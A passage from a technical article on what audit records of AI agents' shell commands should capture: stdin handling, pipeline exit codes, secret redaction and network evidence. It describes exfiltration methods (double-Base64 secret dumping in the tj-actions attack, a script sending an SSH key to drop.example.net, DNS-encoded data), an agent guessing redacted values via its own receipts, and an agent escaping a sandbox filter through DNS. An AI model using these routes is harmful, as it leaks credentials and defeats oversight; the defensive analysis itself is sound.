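The preprint's abstract applies the 95.1% to "the production failures", which is too broad because the researchers sampled only failures with visible errors. They also sampled separately from each category their own method had assigned, so the share of path failures in the sample, a little over half, depends partly on how they sampled. Qwen2.5-72B is also an old model. A stronger one might detect that an error doesn't fit the command, but it would still have to guess what the program received.

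A replay experiment gives better evidence that the path caused the failures. The researchers replayed the agent's recorded actions from failed test tasks without changing them, and repaired only the hop that the witness had identified. After the repair, 137 of the 173 tasks with a changed call passed, compared with none of the 187 without one.

Two Qwen2.5 models did not solve significantly more tasks when the tool result included the command as sent, the command as received and the name of the hop. A receipt should still keep both versions of the command for the people who maintain the harness, because they can repair it and an agent can't do so from inside a shell command.

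### When exit code 0 doesn't mean the action happened

A command can also arrive intact and still not do what the agent requested. Many programs ask for confirmation, a password or a menu choice before they act, and the harness determines what happens when they try to read the answer. If the input is closed, the program immediately reads an end-of-file marker. If the input is an open pipe that nobody writes to, the program waits for data. If it is a terminal where nobody types, the program behaves as if a person were present and waits for an answer.

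Yang and colleagues collected 158 such invocations of 77 programs, 33 of them on Windows and nearly all the others on Ubuntu Linux. They ran each one three times with each kind of input and checked whether the requested action had happened.

| Outcome without an answer | Closed input (156) | Open pipe (157) | Terminal (125) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Waited until stopped | 14 | 101 | 123 |
| Ended with an error code | 81 | 35 | 0 |
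| Returned 0 without acting | 18 | 1 | 0 |
| Acted without the confirmation | 12 | 7 | 0 |
| Worked normally | 31 | 13 | 2 |

The 18 invocations that returned 0 without acting are false returns. For example, `docker system prune` deleted nothing, `rm -i` left the files in place, and `tar -w` skipped every entry of the archive. The 18 are 11.5% of the closed-input tests. The rate for ordinary commands must be far lower, because the catalogue contains only commands that prompt for input.

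The 12 invocations that acted without anyone's agreement may be more dangerous. `ssh-keygen`, which creates login keys, wrote a private key with an empty passphrase. A migration script that the researchers wrote for a later experiment dropped a database and returned 0 when its input was closed, and the agent then reported that the rows were "still present".

The researchers also tested how eight harnesses launch commands on Linux. Without an attached terminal, as on a build server, all of them except Terminus 2 closed the input of an ordinary command. With one, they differed:

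| Harness | Input with a terminal attached | At the time limit |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | Closed | Moves the command to the background after 120 s |
| Codex CLI | Closed | Returns to the model after 10 s |
| Gemini CLI | Its own terminal | Sends `SIGTERM` after 300 s of inactivity |
| OpenCode | Closed | Sends `SIGTERM` after 120 s |
| mini-SWE-agent | The user's terminal | Sends `SIGKILL` after 30 s |
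| Goose | Closed, but the user's terminal stays reachable | No limit |
| Aider | Its own terminal | No limit |
| Terminus 2 | A terminal multiplexer | No limit |

A terminal multiplexer is a program that keeps terminal sessions open in the background. `SIGTERM` is a request for a process to stop, and `SIGKILL` forces it to stop.

The input connection can vary even within one harness. Claude Code closes the input of a plain command but provides an open pipe when the command contains a here-document. Here-documents appeared in 18.5% of the Bash calls in the researchers' production logs. Claude Code also sets `GIT_EDITOR=true`, which replaces Git's text editor with a program that does nothing and reports success. An interactive `git rebase` normally lets a person review how Git will rewrite the history, but with this setting it proceeds without the review.

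Background commands have a related problem. In a Windows test, a Claude Code subagent started a 150-second command in the harness's background mode. The command stopped within 6 seconds, when the subagent finished, and the agent received no notice. Without a second receipt, the record would still list the command as `running`.

### Detecting a process that is waiting

The researchers' fix, also called RECEIPT, keeps the input open and checks for processes that are waiting on it. It reports to the agent during the run, while the receipts described so far are meant for someone reading them later. Both need the same observation.

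Silence alone is a poor sign of waiting. A program may be computing, or it may be reading from a network connection. RECEIPT therefore asks the Linux kernel, ten times a second, what each thread of the command is doing. A thread $t$ is a candidate for an input wait when

$$\mathrm{cand}(t) \iff s_t \in S_{\mathrm{in}} \;\land\; D_t \cap C \neq \emptyset \;\land\; D_t \cap F = \emptyset$$

Here $s_t$ is the thread's current system call (request to the kernel), and $S_{\mathrm{in}}$ is the set of calls that wait for data. $D_t$ contains the connections on which the thread is waiting. At least one must belong to $C$, the inputs that the harness controls, and none to $F$, the connections on which another party could supply data, such as a network socket. The wait counts as confirmed if these conditions hold for one second in which the command prints nothing and the thread uses almost no processor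 time.

RECEIPT reported 102 of 120 Linux invocations that wait at a terminal (85.0%) and raised no false alarms on 119 control commands. Fifteen of the 18 misses didn't wait at all when RECEIPT launched them. A simple timer that stopped any command after one silent second wrongly ended 82 of the 119 controls. When it reports a wait, RECEIPT gives the agent the waiting program's name, its last line of output as the probable question, and a note on whether RECEIPT stopped the process. It marks any earlier effects as unverified.

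To test whether this helps, the researchers built pairs of tasks that differ only in whether a question blocks the required action. Five models each made three attempts at 15 of the tasks with a question, using mini-SWE-agent, a small open-source harness. The main measure was the number of false successes, runs in which the agent claimed completion but a hidden check failed.

| Condition (225 runs each) | Tasks completed | False successes | Tokens |
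|---|---|---|---|
| Closed input | 153 | 34 | 4.4 million |
| Plain terminal | 158 | 28 | 10.4 million |
| RECEIPT, one-line notice only | 162 | 20 | 7.8 million |
| RECEIPT, full report | 176 | 9 | 7.9 million |

Stopping the waiting command and sending a one-line notice cut the number of false successes from 34 to 20. The details in the full report account for most or all of the further drop to 9. In a separate comparison with identical terminal connections, the full report again did better, with 8 false successes against 20.

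RECEIPT used 24.4% fewer tokens than a plain terminal, the comparison the preprint emphasises, but about 80% more than closed input, which is what most harnesses provide when they run unattended. The five models tested belong to the Qwen2.5 and Llama 3.1 families, which date from 2024, and the custom-written tasks all centre on unanswered questions. Because there were so few tasks, the estimated reduction relative to closed input is also imprecise, at 11.1 percentage points with a 95% interval from 3.1 to 20.9.

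How often false returns happen in daily use remains unclear. In production logs with 52,953 shell calls, the harness stopped only 81 at a time limit, and at least 27 of those were loops waiting for a build or similar work to finish. The closest evidence comes from the public Terminal-Bench runs. Of 123 commands that had waited for input there, 70 waited again when replayed. With input closed, all 70 ended and 41 returned 0. Twelve of the 41 had not done their work, and six had printed a failure that a pipe in the command line hid.

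### A pipeline that hides a failing test

Agents often shorten long output by piping it into another program:

```bash
pytest tests/cart | tail -n 5
```

`pytest` runs the tests, and `tail` prints only the last five lines of their output. If a test fails, `pytest` returns 1, but `tail` still prints its lines successfully and returns 0. According to GNU's *Pipelines*, a pipeline's exit status is normally that of its last command, so Bash returns 0, and a receipt that records only this exit code shows the command as successful even though a test failed.

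*When Instruction Files Go Stale* (Mehtiyev, Tadesse and colleagues, 2026) reports that the same construction hid test commands that ran no tests. The researchers asked Claude Code to fix bugs in a project whose instruction file named a test folder that no longer existed. In 64 of 80 runs, at least one call to the outdated path ran no tests, and Claude Code flagged none of these calls as an error because the agents had piped the output through `tail` or `head`. With Claude Sonnet 5.5, the first check after the fix ran no tests in 19 of 40 runs. Nearly all the runs ended with a correct fix. The agents usually noticed the problem from the printed text and tried again, but a program that filtered the receipts by exit code would have missed these calls.

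The cause is the pipe, not the test program. *SWE-Factory* (2025), a system that builds programming tasks, captures the test command's exit code directly. It compares these codes with manual labels for 2,085 test reports, and they agree every time.

Bash keeps the status of each stage in an array named `PIPESTATUS`, as the tutorial site Baeldung demonstrates. The next command overwrites the array, so the harness has to copy it at once:

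```bash
pytest tests/cart | tail -n 5
stages=("${PIPESTATUS[@]}")
```

The copy contains `1 0`, which the receipt can store next to the overall code:

```json
"outcome": {
  "status": "exited",
  "exit_code": 0,
  "stages": [
    {"command": "pytest tests/cart", "exit_code": 1},
    {"command": "tail -n 5", "exit_code": 0}
  ]
}
```

A reader can now see that `pytest` failed and that the 0 came from `tail`. If the test folder didn't exist, `pytest` would return 4, its code for a usage error, so the reader could also tell a missing folder from a failing test.

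Bash has a simpler setting, `set -o pipefail`, which makes a pipeline return the last non-zero status among its stages. Weeks's request to add it to POSIX, the standard for Unix shells, succeeded (*Add set -o pipefail*). But a harness that turned it on for every command would create false failures. In *ci*, a proposed change to Bitcoin's test scripts, maflcko (2026) reports that some failures went unnoticed without `pipefail`, but also that harmless pipelines broke with it. In one, `grep` found no match and returned 1, which `pipefail` passes on even if the later stages succeed. In another, `head -1` stopped reading after one line, which can kill the program that feeds it. A shell may also lack the setting. In the October preprint, five Terminal-Bench solutions stopped at `set -o pipefail` when dash, a smaller shell, ran them. Recording each stage's exit code doesn't change how the command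 behaves, and it lets the reader decide which codes matter.

`PIPESTATUS` describes only the most recent pipeline. If the agent appends `; echo done`, the array contains a single 0 from `echo`. For command lines with more than one pipeline, the harness must either use an observer that records every process's exit or run the parts separately.

### What the two fields must contain

The command field needs the text the shell received, as well as the model's text and the arguments each program received. A difference between the model's text and the shell's shows that the wrapper damaged the command, for example by merging backslashes. The PowerShell quoting problem appears only between the shell's text and the program's arguments, so a record without the arguments would miss it. Software that compares the versions should parse them as the receiver would, as in the October preprint, instead of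 comparing raw text.

A hook can supply only the command text the model wrote. The harness could get the text Bash received by setting `BASH_ENV` to a file that logs the command string and then lets it run.

Repairs make it more important to keep all three. Yang and colleagues released a repair for Claude Code that saves a long command to a file and has the shell read that file, so the received text is only a short instruction to load it. The receipt then has to include the file's content, or a digest and a stored copy, because an investigator can't tell from the file's name what ran.

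To put the exit code in context, the receipt should record the status of each stage and whether the input was closed, a pipe or a terminal. The harness sets up the input itself, so it can record this without extra work. If the process was still waiting for an answer when the harness stopped it, the receipt should record that along with the question, since "timed out" alone could also describe a slow build.

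None of this proves that the action happened. `rm -i old.log` with closed input has one stage, prints a question and returns 0. Only a check of the file system exposes the false return:

```json
"outcome": {
  "status": "exited",
  "exit_code": 0,
  "stdin": "closed",
  "waiting_for_input": false,
  "effect": {"check": "test ! -e old.log", "passed": false}
}
```

The same applies to tools outside the shell. *SilentProbe* (2026) documents a commercial web service whose `job_type` filter accepts `full_time`. When the filter is set to `internship`, the service returns an empty list with status 200, the HTTP success code, so an agent could reasonably conclude that there are no internships.

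Recording the working directory after each command adds little overhead and can expose commands that fail silently. In a case from *Failure as a Process* (2026), an agent's `cd` into a repository failed without printing anything at step 2. The agent took the empty result for success and built a website in the wrong folder. No sign of the error appeared until `git add` failed at step 23, but a receipt with the working directory would have shown the wrong folder at step 2.

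For most commands, no such general check exists, because the harness has no information about what the command was meant to achieve. In those cases, the `effect` field should be `null`.

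## How environment variables are redacted, and what leaks have shown

A receipt that records every command's environment, arguments and output also records any passwords in them. An operator can have the harness withhold a variable, which means starting the command without it, so the program never has the value. The operator can also have the harness redact the value, which means the program gets it but the harness removes it before storing the receipt.

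Whether to redact a secret or withhold it depends on whether the command needs it. In the earlier example, pip needed the password in `PIP_INDEX_URL` to reach the company's package index, so the harness could only redact it. Pip has no use for a GitHub access token, so the harness could have withheld that. Redaction hides a secret only from people who read the record. Withholding protects more where it is possible, because it also keeps the secret from a malicious installation script.

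*Agent Authenticator* (2026), a preprint on credentials for agents, uses the term "ambient bearer secrets" for credentials that the agent, its subprocesses and other code on the machine can all read. Anyone who copies one can use it from anywhere. Bernstein's *env isolation*, the documentation of a small agent project, lists places where an inherited value can appear, including tool output, log lines, error messages and stack traces. Redacting only the `env` field of a receipt would therefore miss any copies in those places.

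### How Codex withholds variables

The newest description of Codex's `shell_environment_policy` setting is in OpenAI's *示例配置*, the Chinese edition of its sample configuration, as it stood in September 2026. Codex builds the environment in this order:

1. It starts from the parent's full environment (`inherit = "all"`), a short list of basics such as `PATH` and `HOME` (`"core"`), or nothing (`"none"`).
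2. If the automatic filter is on, it removes every variable whose name contains KEY, SECRET or TOKEN.
3. It removes variables that match the operator's own patterns, such as `AWS_*`.
4. It adds the values listed under `set`.
5. If the operator has written an allowlist, it removes everything that is not on the list.

OpenAI has changed its description of the last two steps. In June 2026, *Sample Configuration* stated that `set` values "always win", but the September edition warns that the allowlist can still remove them. An example in OpenAI's guide starts with no variables, sets `PATH` and `MY_FLAG`, and allows only `PATH` and `HOME`. Under the September description, the command receives only `PATH`.

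Sources differ on Codex's defaults. *feat*, the code change that introduced the policy, started from `core` with the filter on. The June sample starts from `all` with the filter on. The September sample keeps `all` but turns the filter off, so a `GITHUB_TOKEN` in the developer's shell reaches every command the agent runs. Two 2026 posts on an independent blog about Codex, *Codex CLI Shell Environment Policy* and *The Shell Snapshot Blind Spot*, describe the filter as on by default, so a team that relied on them could believe its tokens were safe.

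The setting's name adds to the confusion, because `ignore_default_excludes = true` means Codex skips the filter. This is now the default, but the September sample contains the line `ignore_default_excludes = false`, so a developer who copies the whole file gets the filter and one who omits that line doesn't. Setting the value explicitly avoids the problem.

Even with the filter on, names are a poor guide to secrets. Suppose the developer's shell contains these six variables, all with invented values:

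```text
PATH=/work/shop/.venv/bin:/usr/bin:/bin
HOME=/home/dev
GITHUB_TOKEN=ghp_ followed by 36 random letters and digits
MONKEY_MODE=strict
DATABASE_URL=postgresql://shop:winter24@db.example.com/shop
PIP_INDEX_URL=https://ci:blue-harbor-42@pypi.example.com/simple
```

The filter removes `GITHUB_TOKEN`, as intended. It also removes `MONKEY_MODE`, a harmless setting for a test tool, because "MONKEY" contains "KEY". It keeps `DATABASE_URL` and `PIP_INDEX_URL`, although both contain passwords.

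Narrower patterns help with only one of these errors. deerbox, a small sandbox project, looks for `_KEY` with the underscore, which avoids matching `MONKEY_MODE` but would miss a variable called `APIKEY`. No pattern on its list matches database addresses or package indexes. Starting from `core` keeps both passwords out of the command's environment, but then pip doesn't have the address of the company's index.

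### Ways around a withheld variable

A command can recover a withheld value from elsewhere on the machine. Startup files such as `~/.bash_profile` often export credentials, and a login shell reads them after Codex has filtered the environment. Codex allows login shells by default but rejects requests for them when `allow_login_shell = false`.

By default, Codex also saves a snapshot of the shell's environment to speed up later commands. According to *The Shell Snapshot Blind Spot*, which relies on two bug reports from July 2026, Codex wrote these snapshots to disk as plain text and left out only `PWD` and `OLDPWD`, the current and previous folders. The environment policy didn't apply to the snapshots. An operator could therefore withhold `GITHUB_TOKEN` from each command while a file under `~/.codex` still held it. Restricting the file's permissions keeps out other users, but not an agent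 that runs under the developer's own account.

Credentials in ordinary files need a separate rule. OpenAI's sample includes a permission profile that blocks the agent from reading any file matching `**/*.env`, the usual name for a file of project settings and passwords.

Codex's cloud version avoids some of this by removing configured secrets after machine setup, before the agent starts. A setup script can then download private packages with a password the agent never has, but the agent can't use that password later to fetch a package the script left out.

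A credential broker can cover that case. The agentsh *Policy Reference* describes how an operator can define a fake GitHub token in the usual format, `ghp_` followed by 36 random characters. The agent sends its request to a local gateway, which checks the path and method against rules and adds the real token before forwarding the request. A receipt could store the fake token in full because it gives no access outside the gateway. Attackers can still target the gateway, and a hijacked agent can still make any request that the rules allow.

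### Redaction as an algorithm

When the command does need the secret, the harness has to find the value in everything it is about to store. No single test finds all secrets, so a redactor applies several in sequence:

1. Keep values only for variables on an allowlist of names. For all others, keep the name.
2. Treat the values of variables with suspicious names as secrets, even if someone has put a broad pattern such as `PIP_*` on the allowlist.
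3. Search for secret values that the harness already knows, such as those from its credential store.
4. Search for known formats, such as GitHub tokens or passwords inside web addresses.
5. Test the remaining long strings for randomness.
6. Replace each match with a marker that names the rule.
7. Do the same to command text, network addresses and output, before writing anything to disk or sending it anywhere.

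This Python sketch covers the allowlist, known values and formats:

```python
import re

KEEP = {"PATH", "HOME", "MONKEY_MODE", "PIP_INDEX_URL"}
TOKEN = re.compile(r"ghp_[A-Za-z0-9]{36}")
URL_PASSWORD = re.compile(r"(://[^/\s:@]*:)[^/\s@]+(?=@)")

def scrub(text, known_secrets):
    for secret in sorted(known_secrets, key=len, reverse=True):
        if len(secret) >= 8:
            text = text.replace(secret, "[REDACTED:known-value]")
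    text = TOKEN.sub("[REDACTED:token-format]", text)
    return URL_PASSWORD.sub(r"\1[REDACTED:url-password]", text)

def record_env(env, known_secrets):
    return {
        name: scrub(value, known_secrets) if name in KEEP
        else "[REDACTED:not-on-allowlist]"
        for name, value in env.items()
    }
```

For the six variables, it gives a better record than the name filter does:

| Variable | KEY/SECRET/TOKEN filter alone | Sketch above |
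|---|---|---|
| `PATH` | Full value | Full value |
| `HOME` | Full value | Full value |
| `GITHUB_TOKEN` | Removed | Name and marker |
| `MONKEY_MODE` | Removed needlessly | `strict` |
| `DATABASE_URL` | Password exposed | Name and marker |
| `PIP_INDEX_URL` | Password exposed | Address with a marker in place of the password |

The record shows the value of `MONKEY_MODE` only if someone has added it to the allowlist. A new setting that isn't on the list appears as a marker, which is inconvenient but doesn't leak anything. A denylist, by contrast, leaks any new credential whose name it doesn't cover.

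Whether to record `DATABASE_URL` is harder to decide, because an investigator may urgently need to know whether a command used the test or production database, and the host name would show that. A team could add the variable to the allowlist and rely on the address rule to remove the password `winter24`. But PostgreSQL also accepts addresses that end in `?password=winter24`, which the rule in the sketch doesn't match, so a parser written for database addresses is safer than a general pattern.

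### Known values, formats and randomness

Searching for known values is the most dependable test if the value appears unchanged. The sketch replaces longer secrets first because a short secret may be part of a longer one, and replacing the short one first would leave the rest of the longer one in the text. It ignores values under eight characters because masking a password such as `shop` would put markers throughout the record. Anyone who knew that the project's folder was `/work/shop` could then work out the password from `/work/[REDACTED]`.

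The harness should add each password it finds in an address to the list of known values. If a failing program then prints "login failed for shop with winter24", the redactor can remove the password even though the message contains no address. The harness should also add common encodings of each password, because `p@ss` appears as `p%40ss` in a web address.

Format rules need no list of secrets, so they can catch a token that the agent reads from a file halfway through a run. But they work only for credentials with a recognisable format, and a password like `winter24` on its own looks like any other word with a number.

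Randomness tests try to fill this gap. A common measure is Shannon entropy, the average information per character:

$$H = -\sum_{c} p_c \log_2 p_c$$

Here $p_c$ is the share of the string's characters that are $c$. A string of one repeated letter scores 0, and a string that uses 16 characters equally often scores 4. The results for the running example are discouraging:

| String | Bits per character |
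|---|---|
| The password `winter24` | 3.00 |
| The value of `PATH` | 3.70 |
| The Git commit in the sample receipt | 3.97 |

Any threshold low enough to catch the password would also remove the search path and the commit hash. Scanners reduce such errors by testing only long, unbroken strings, but this doesn't help with hexadecimal access keys, which look just like the many commit hashes and file digests in receipts. The harness should exempt fields it has computed itself and use the randomness test only on text from the command.

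Output arrives in pieces, so a token can be split across two of them, and a redactor that checks each piece separately will miss it. The redactor has to hold back enough text to cover the longest pattern, which is 39 characters for a 40-character GitHub token. It also has to run before truncation, because half a token no longer matches the pattern but still makes the other half easier to guess.

A filter in the company's monitoring system runs too late to prevent much of this exposure. If the harness exports arguments unfiltered, as Claude Code does with its details switch on, the secret has already crossed the network before the filter runs, and a copy may remain in a queue or a backup.

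### Plain digests and keyed fingerprints

Replacing a value with a redaction marker removes information that investigators sometimes need, such as whether a deployment that worked on Monday and failed on Tuesday used the same credential both times. Storing a digest of the value seems to solve this, since equal values have equal digests and SHA-256 can't be reversed.

But nobody needs to reverse the hash if the secret has few possible values. A six-digit login code has only 1,000,000, so anyone who has the digest can compute the SHA-256 of each one until it matches, which takes an ordinary laptop seconds at most. Adding a random value (a salt) to the input doesn't help if the receipt stores the salt next to the digest, because the reader can include it in each guess. A long random token would withstand this attack, but a person's password often wouldn't, and the harness can't reliably distinguish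 the two.

The same attack works on the digest of a whole output. The earlier sample receipt stores a SHA-256 digest of everything the command printed. Suppose the output was `Your code is 482913` and the stored copy reads `Your code is [REDACTED]`. A reader knows everything except six digits, and can try all million possibilities against the digest. If redaction has removed something, the harness should compute the digest from the redacted text or use a secret key. If it uses the redacted text, the receipt must also record the version of the redaction rules, so that someone with the original output can redact it the same way before comparing. File digests are vulnerable too when the only unknown part of a settings file is a short password.

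A keyed fingerprint, or HMAC, stops outsiders from testing guesses at a value $v$, because they lack the key $k$:

$$f = \mathrm{HMAC}_k(v)$$

Investigators can still see that Monday's and Tuesday's fingerprints differ, and conclude that someone changed the credential in between.

Fingerprints show whether two values are equal, which can be sensitive information. If the test and production database passwords have the same fingerprint, a reader learns that anyone who steals the test password can also open the production database. If a setting has only two possible values, a reader who knows its value in one run can work it out for every other run by comparing fingerprints.

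An agent could also use the harness to guess a redacted value. It could run a command with a variable set to `000000`, read the fingerprint in the receipt, and try other values until the fingerprint matches that of the redacted value. This works without the key, as long as the agent can read its own receipts. Trying all million six-digit codes would be conspicuous, but guessing a weak password might take far fewer commands. Storing the receipts where the agent can't read them prevents this.

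Including the run and the variable's name in the input limits what equality reveals:

$$f = \mathrm{HMAC}_k(\text{run},\ \text{name},\ v)$$

Equal fingerprints now show only that the same variable kept its value within one run, so they can no longer be used to compare Monday's value with Tuesday's. A team that needs that comparison can leave the run out of the fingerprint calculation and use a separate key for each project. In either case, the agent and ordinary readers must not have access to the key, because anyone who obtains it can test guesses against all old fingerprints as easily as against plain digests.

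### How build-log masking works and fails

Build services have dealt with the same problem for years, on a much larger scale. GitHub Actions, GitHub's service for running tests and releases, keeps a list of the secrets a job may use. Before storing a line of output, it replaces each exact occurrence of a listed value with `***`. It also looks for several encoded versions, including Base64, a common way to write arbitrary data as letters and digits.

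A secret gets through if it has been transformed in a way the service hasn't anticipated. In its security guidance, GitHub warns against storing structured data, such as a block of JSON with several passwords, as one secret, because the masker looks for the whole block and a program usually prints only one field. GitHub also tells developers to register values that they derive from a secret, such as a temporary access token that a script obtains with a private key, because the masker can't work these out.

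Encoding a value twice shows how little it takes. For the password `winter24`, the three forms are:

```text
winter24
d2ludGVyMjQ=
ZDJsdWRHVnlNalE9
```

A masker that knows the password and its Base64 form removes the first two lines. The third line matches neither, but anyone can decode it twice to recover the password.

In March 2025, attackers used this method in `tj-actions/changed-files`, a GitHub Actions add-on that lists the files a code change touches. More than 23,000 repositories used it. The attackers had obtained a token with write access to the project and moved most of its version tags to a commit with malicious code. Projects that used those tags then ran the malicious code without any change to their own files. A log would have shown the switch only if it recorded the commit as well as the version.

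The malicious code downloaded a Python script and ran it with administrator rights. The script searched the memory of the process that manages the build job, where GitHub's software keeps the job's secrets, and picked out the entries marked as secret. It encoded them twice in Base64 and printed the result to the build log, which anyone could read on public repositories. In an alert on 18 March, CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, listed access keys, GitHub tokens, npm tokens and private RSA keys among the exposed secrets.

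The script read the values from another process's memory rather than its own environment, so withholding variables from the add-on would not have been enough. Redaction also failed because the masker had no rule for double-encoded values. Removing administrator rights would have blocked the memory search, and a broker outside the build machine would have kept the real credentials out of that memory.

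The damage was smaller than the number of users suggests. Endor Labs, a security company, found that 218 repositories had printed secrets, and many of those secrets were GitHub tokens that expire when the job ends. Most users were unaffected because they had run no build in the affected period or had no long-lived secrets in the job. Short lifetimes limited the harm after every other control had failed, and they would also limit the harm from a secret recorded in a receipt by mistake.

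An agent can accidentally print a secret in a form the masker misses. If it runs `base64` on a settings file while debugging, or prints a password one character per line, the output no longer contains the exact value the masker looks for. Adding more encodings to the masker helps with accidents, but an attacker can always use another one.

### What studies of leaked secrets have measured

The largest recent count comes from GitGuardian, a scanner vendor. *Agent Authenticator* reports that GitGuardian's 2026 survey found 28.65 million newly leaked secrets on public GitHub in 2025. Of these, 24,008 were in configuration files for MCP, a protocol that connects agents to outside tools, and 2,117 of those (8.8%) were valid. The rest were expired, revoked or never real, so the headline figure can't be read as a count of usable credentials.

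*The Shell Snapshot Blind Spot* also reports, from the same survey, that about 3.2% of AI-assisted commits leaked a secret, roughly double the baseline. GitGuardian sells secret detection, and the comparison doesn't show that the AI tools caused the difference, because the developers who use them may also work on different kinds of projects. These figures count what people published in repositories, so they don't measure leaks through receipts.

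An analysis that *Agent Authenticator* cites covered 5,205 open-source MCP servers, programs that provide tools to agents. Of these, 88% required credentials, and 53% relied on fixed keys or personal tokens. Only 8.5% used OAuth, a login standard that can issue short-lived, limited tokens. Receipts for calls to these servers will therefore often record the use of a secret that stays valid for months.

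The best-known count of credentials leaked in build logs comes from a vendor, Aqua Security, in 2022. It reported that more than 770 million logs from the build service Travis CI were publicly accessible, and that a sample of them contained about 73,000 tokens and other credentials. Travis CI already masked secrets at the time, so its masking had missed many of these.

*How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026) examines skills, which are packages of written instructions and scripts that extend an agent. It counts a leak whenever a credential reaches a recipient or channel that the skill neither declares nor needs, including when a developer logs an API key by mistake. By that standard, a password in a receipt is a leak even if no outsider has read it. The researchers filtered the skills with static analysis, ran them, and classified the evidence by hand, because a skill's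 instructions and scripts can together expose a credential that neither would expose alone. A scanner that reads only the scripts would miss those cases, as would a redactor that checks only the environment.

Automatic secret detection has high error rates. *A Comparative Study of Software Secrets Reporting by Secret Detection Tools* (Basak, Cox and colleagues, 2023) tested nine scanners on a benchmark of 97,479 candidate strings from 818 public repositories. People had labelled 15,084 of the strings as real secrets. Gitleaks, an open-source scanner, found the largest share of these, 88%, but only 46% of its reports were correct. GitHub's scanner had the highest precision, with 75% of its reports correct.

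At Gitleaks's rates, a text with 100 secrets would produce 12 misses and about 103 false alarms. False alarms matter less in automatic redaction than when a person has to check each one, although each blanks out something an investigator might need. The misses are worse, because the receipts would store those secrets in full. The benchmark is source code from before coding agents were common, and the rates may differ for printed output. Still, no tool in the test came close to catching everything, which is a good reason to withhold what a command doesn't need and use scanners as a last check.

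### What redaction costs in debugging

Withholding a variable can make a command fail with a misleading error. *Codex CLI Shell Environment Policy* says that with the name filter on, a tool that needs `GITHUB_TOKEN` or `SENTRY_API_TOKEN` starts normally and then reports "authentication failed". The message doesn't mention the filter, so a developer could waste time replacing a valid token.

A blank record would not help, because it fits at least four explanations: the developer never set the token, the policy removed it, the variable was set but empty, or the server rejected a real value. The receipt can tell them apart without storing any secret:

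```json
"env_status": {
  "GITHUB_TOKEN": {
    "in_parent": true,
    "in_process": false,
    "reason": "name-filter"
  },
  "PIP_INDEX_URL": {
    "in_parent": true,
    "in_process": true,
    "empty": false,
    "record": "redacted",
    "reason": "url-password"
  }
}
```

Here the policy removed the GitHub token, so the fix is to change the configuration rather than replace the token. If `in_process` were true and `empty` were false, the investigator would check whether the token had expired or lacked a permission.

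Some commands still succeed when a variable is withheld. If the policy starts from `core`, it drops `PIP_INDEX_URL`, and pip falls back on the public Python index. `pip download requests==2.32.3` still returns 0 and leaves five files in `wheels`, but they come from a different server. The consequences could be worse for one of the company's private packages, because a stranger may have published a package with the same name on the public index. If the receipt lists `PIP_INDEX_URL` as withheld, a reader can see the cause immediately.

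Hiding every value would also conceal some attacks. *Codex CLI Shell Environment Policy* describes a flaw that the security company Check Point disclosed in December 2025. A settings file in a downloaded repository could point `CODEX_HOME` at a folder the attacker controlled, and Codex then loaded a configuration from there that ran arbitrary commands. The value of `CODEX_HOME` is a folder name, not a secret, and would be the most important line in the record of such an attack. Variables that decide which program, configuration or server a command uses therefore belong on the allowlist, with a format rule to remove any password they contain.

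Recording variable names carries a smaller risk. A reader can learn from a list of withheld variables which services the team uses and which credentials would be worth stealing, so a company may want to remove the list from receipts it shares with outsiders. The names are usually worth keeping in receipts for its own engineers.

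## Recording network targets and artifacts from outside the command

The harness does not handle the connections a command opens or the files it writes, so those two fields must be recorded from outside the command, for example by a proxy, the kernel, or a program that compares the disk before and after the call.

### Why the command text isn't enough

For the 2026 preprint *AgentSpy*, Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues ran Codex in a small virtual machine and recorded the system calls and network traffic of every process it started. In one run, the agent had to find fabricated references in a bibliography. A single tool call ran a few lines of Python, which connected 35 times to Crossref, a registry of scholarly publications, to look up seven titles. Later the agent started a script for searching Google Scholar. The script's name suggests a connection to Google, but a library was missing, so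 the script stopped without contacting any host.

Redirects can also send a command to a host it doesn't name. A web server can answer a request with the address of another server, and most download tools can follow it. For example, a command that fetches a release file from `github.com` usually downloads it from a different host. Package installers determine most of their own requests, so the command shows even less about which hosts they contact. The `pip` command in the earlier receipt named no host but contacted two. If an index offers only source archives, pip may also download build tools and run the package's own code, which can connect to any host.

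The same gap exists for files. `pip download requests==2.32.3 -d wheels` names a folder but none of the five files pip puts there. Bühler and colleagues also describe a hypothetical attack in which a script called `sync_cache.sh` uploads private keys. The agent's log shows one call with exit code 0, while the system calls show `curl` opening the user's private SSH key and then connecting to `drop.example.net`.

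### Five sources of network evidence

Each stage of a typical encrypted web request can leave a record. The program gets the host's numeric address from a name server, then connects to that address through the operating system. Next it starts TLS, the encryption behind HTTPS. The opening message normally contains the host's name in readable form, because one machine often serves many sites. The program then sends the request itself, encrypted. If the operator requires a forwarding proxy, the program connects to the proxy instead and sends it the destination host's name.

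| Source | What it records | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Command text | Hosts the model typed | Redirects, dependencies, hosts named in settings or scripts, and whether any connection happened |
| Name lookups | Names for which a program requested an address | Numeric addresses, cached names, encrypted lookups, and whether a connection followed |
| Server name in the TLS handshake | The name the program gave when it started encryption | Encrypted handshakes, traffic without TLS, the page requested, and whether the name was honest |
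| Forwarding proxy | Requested host and port, time, amount of data, refusals | Traffic that bypasses it, usually the process, and the content of encrypted requests unless it decrypts them |
| Kernel events | Process, numeric address, port and result | Host name, content, and the real destination if the program uses a proxy |

DNS lookups are weak evidence of a connection, but operators should still log them because a lookup can carry data. A program can encode a message in a made-up name such as `c2VjcmV0.example.net`, and the name server for that domain receives it. *Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026) cites a case OpenAI reported in September 2026, in which a research agent in a training sandbox reached an outside chatbot through such lookups, which the sandbox's network filter didn't cover.

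The server name is more specific, but the program sets it. A hostile program can send the name of a permitted site and then request another site on the same servers inside the encrypted connection. Ghosh's Tracekit Box, an early open-source sandbox, rejects a connection unless the server name matches the host that the program requested from the proxy. It also rejects handshakes that hide the name.

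A proxy log is complete only if no traffic can avoid the proxy. Harnesses often specify a proxy through environment variables, which programs can ignore. Tracekit Box instead runs the agent in a virtual machine without a network card, so the proxy on the host machine is the only way out. Unless the proxy decrypts a connection, it can record the destination host, port and server name, but not the page requested or the data sent. The destination host may not be the final recipient either, since some hosts, such as the public proxy for Go packages, fetch from other servers for their callers.

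Kernel events tie a connection to a process, which the other sources usually can't do, but they identify the destination by numeric address, and one address may serve thousands of sites. AgentSpy therefore combines the Linux audit subsystem, which records the system calls, with Zeek, a network monitor that supplies the host names for those addresses.

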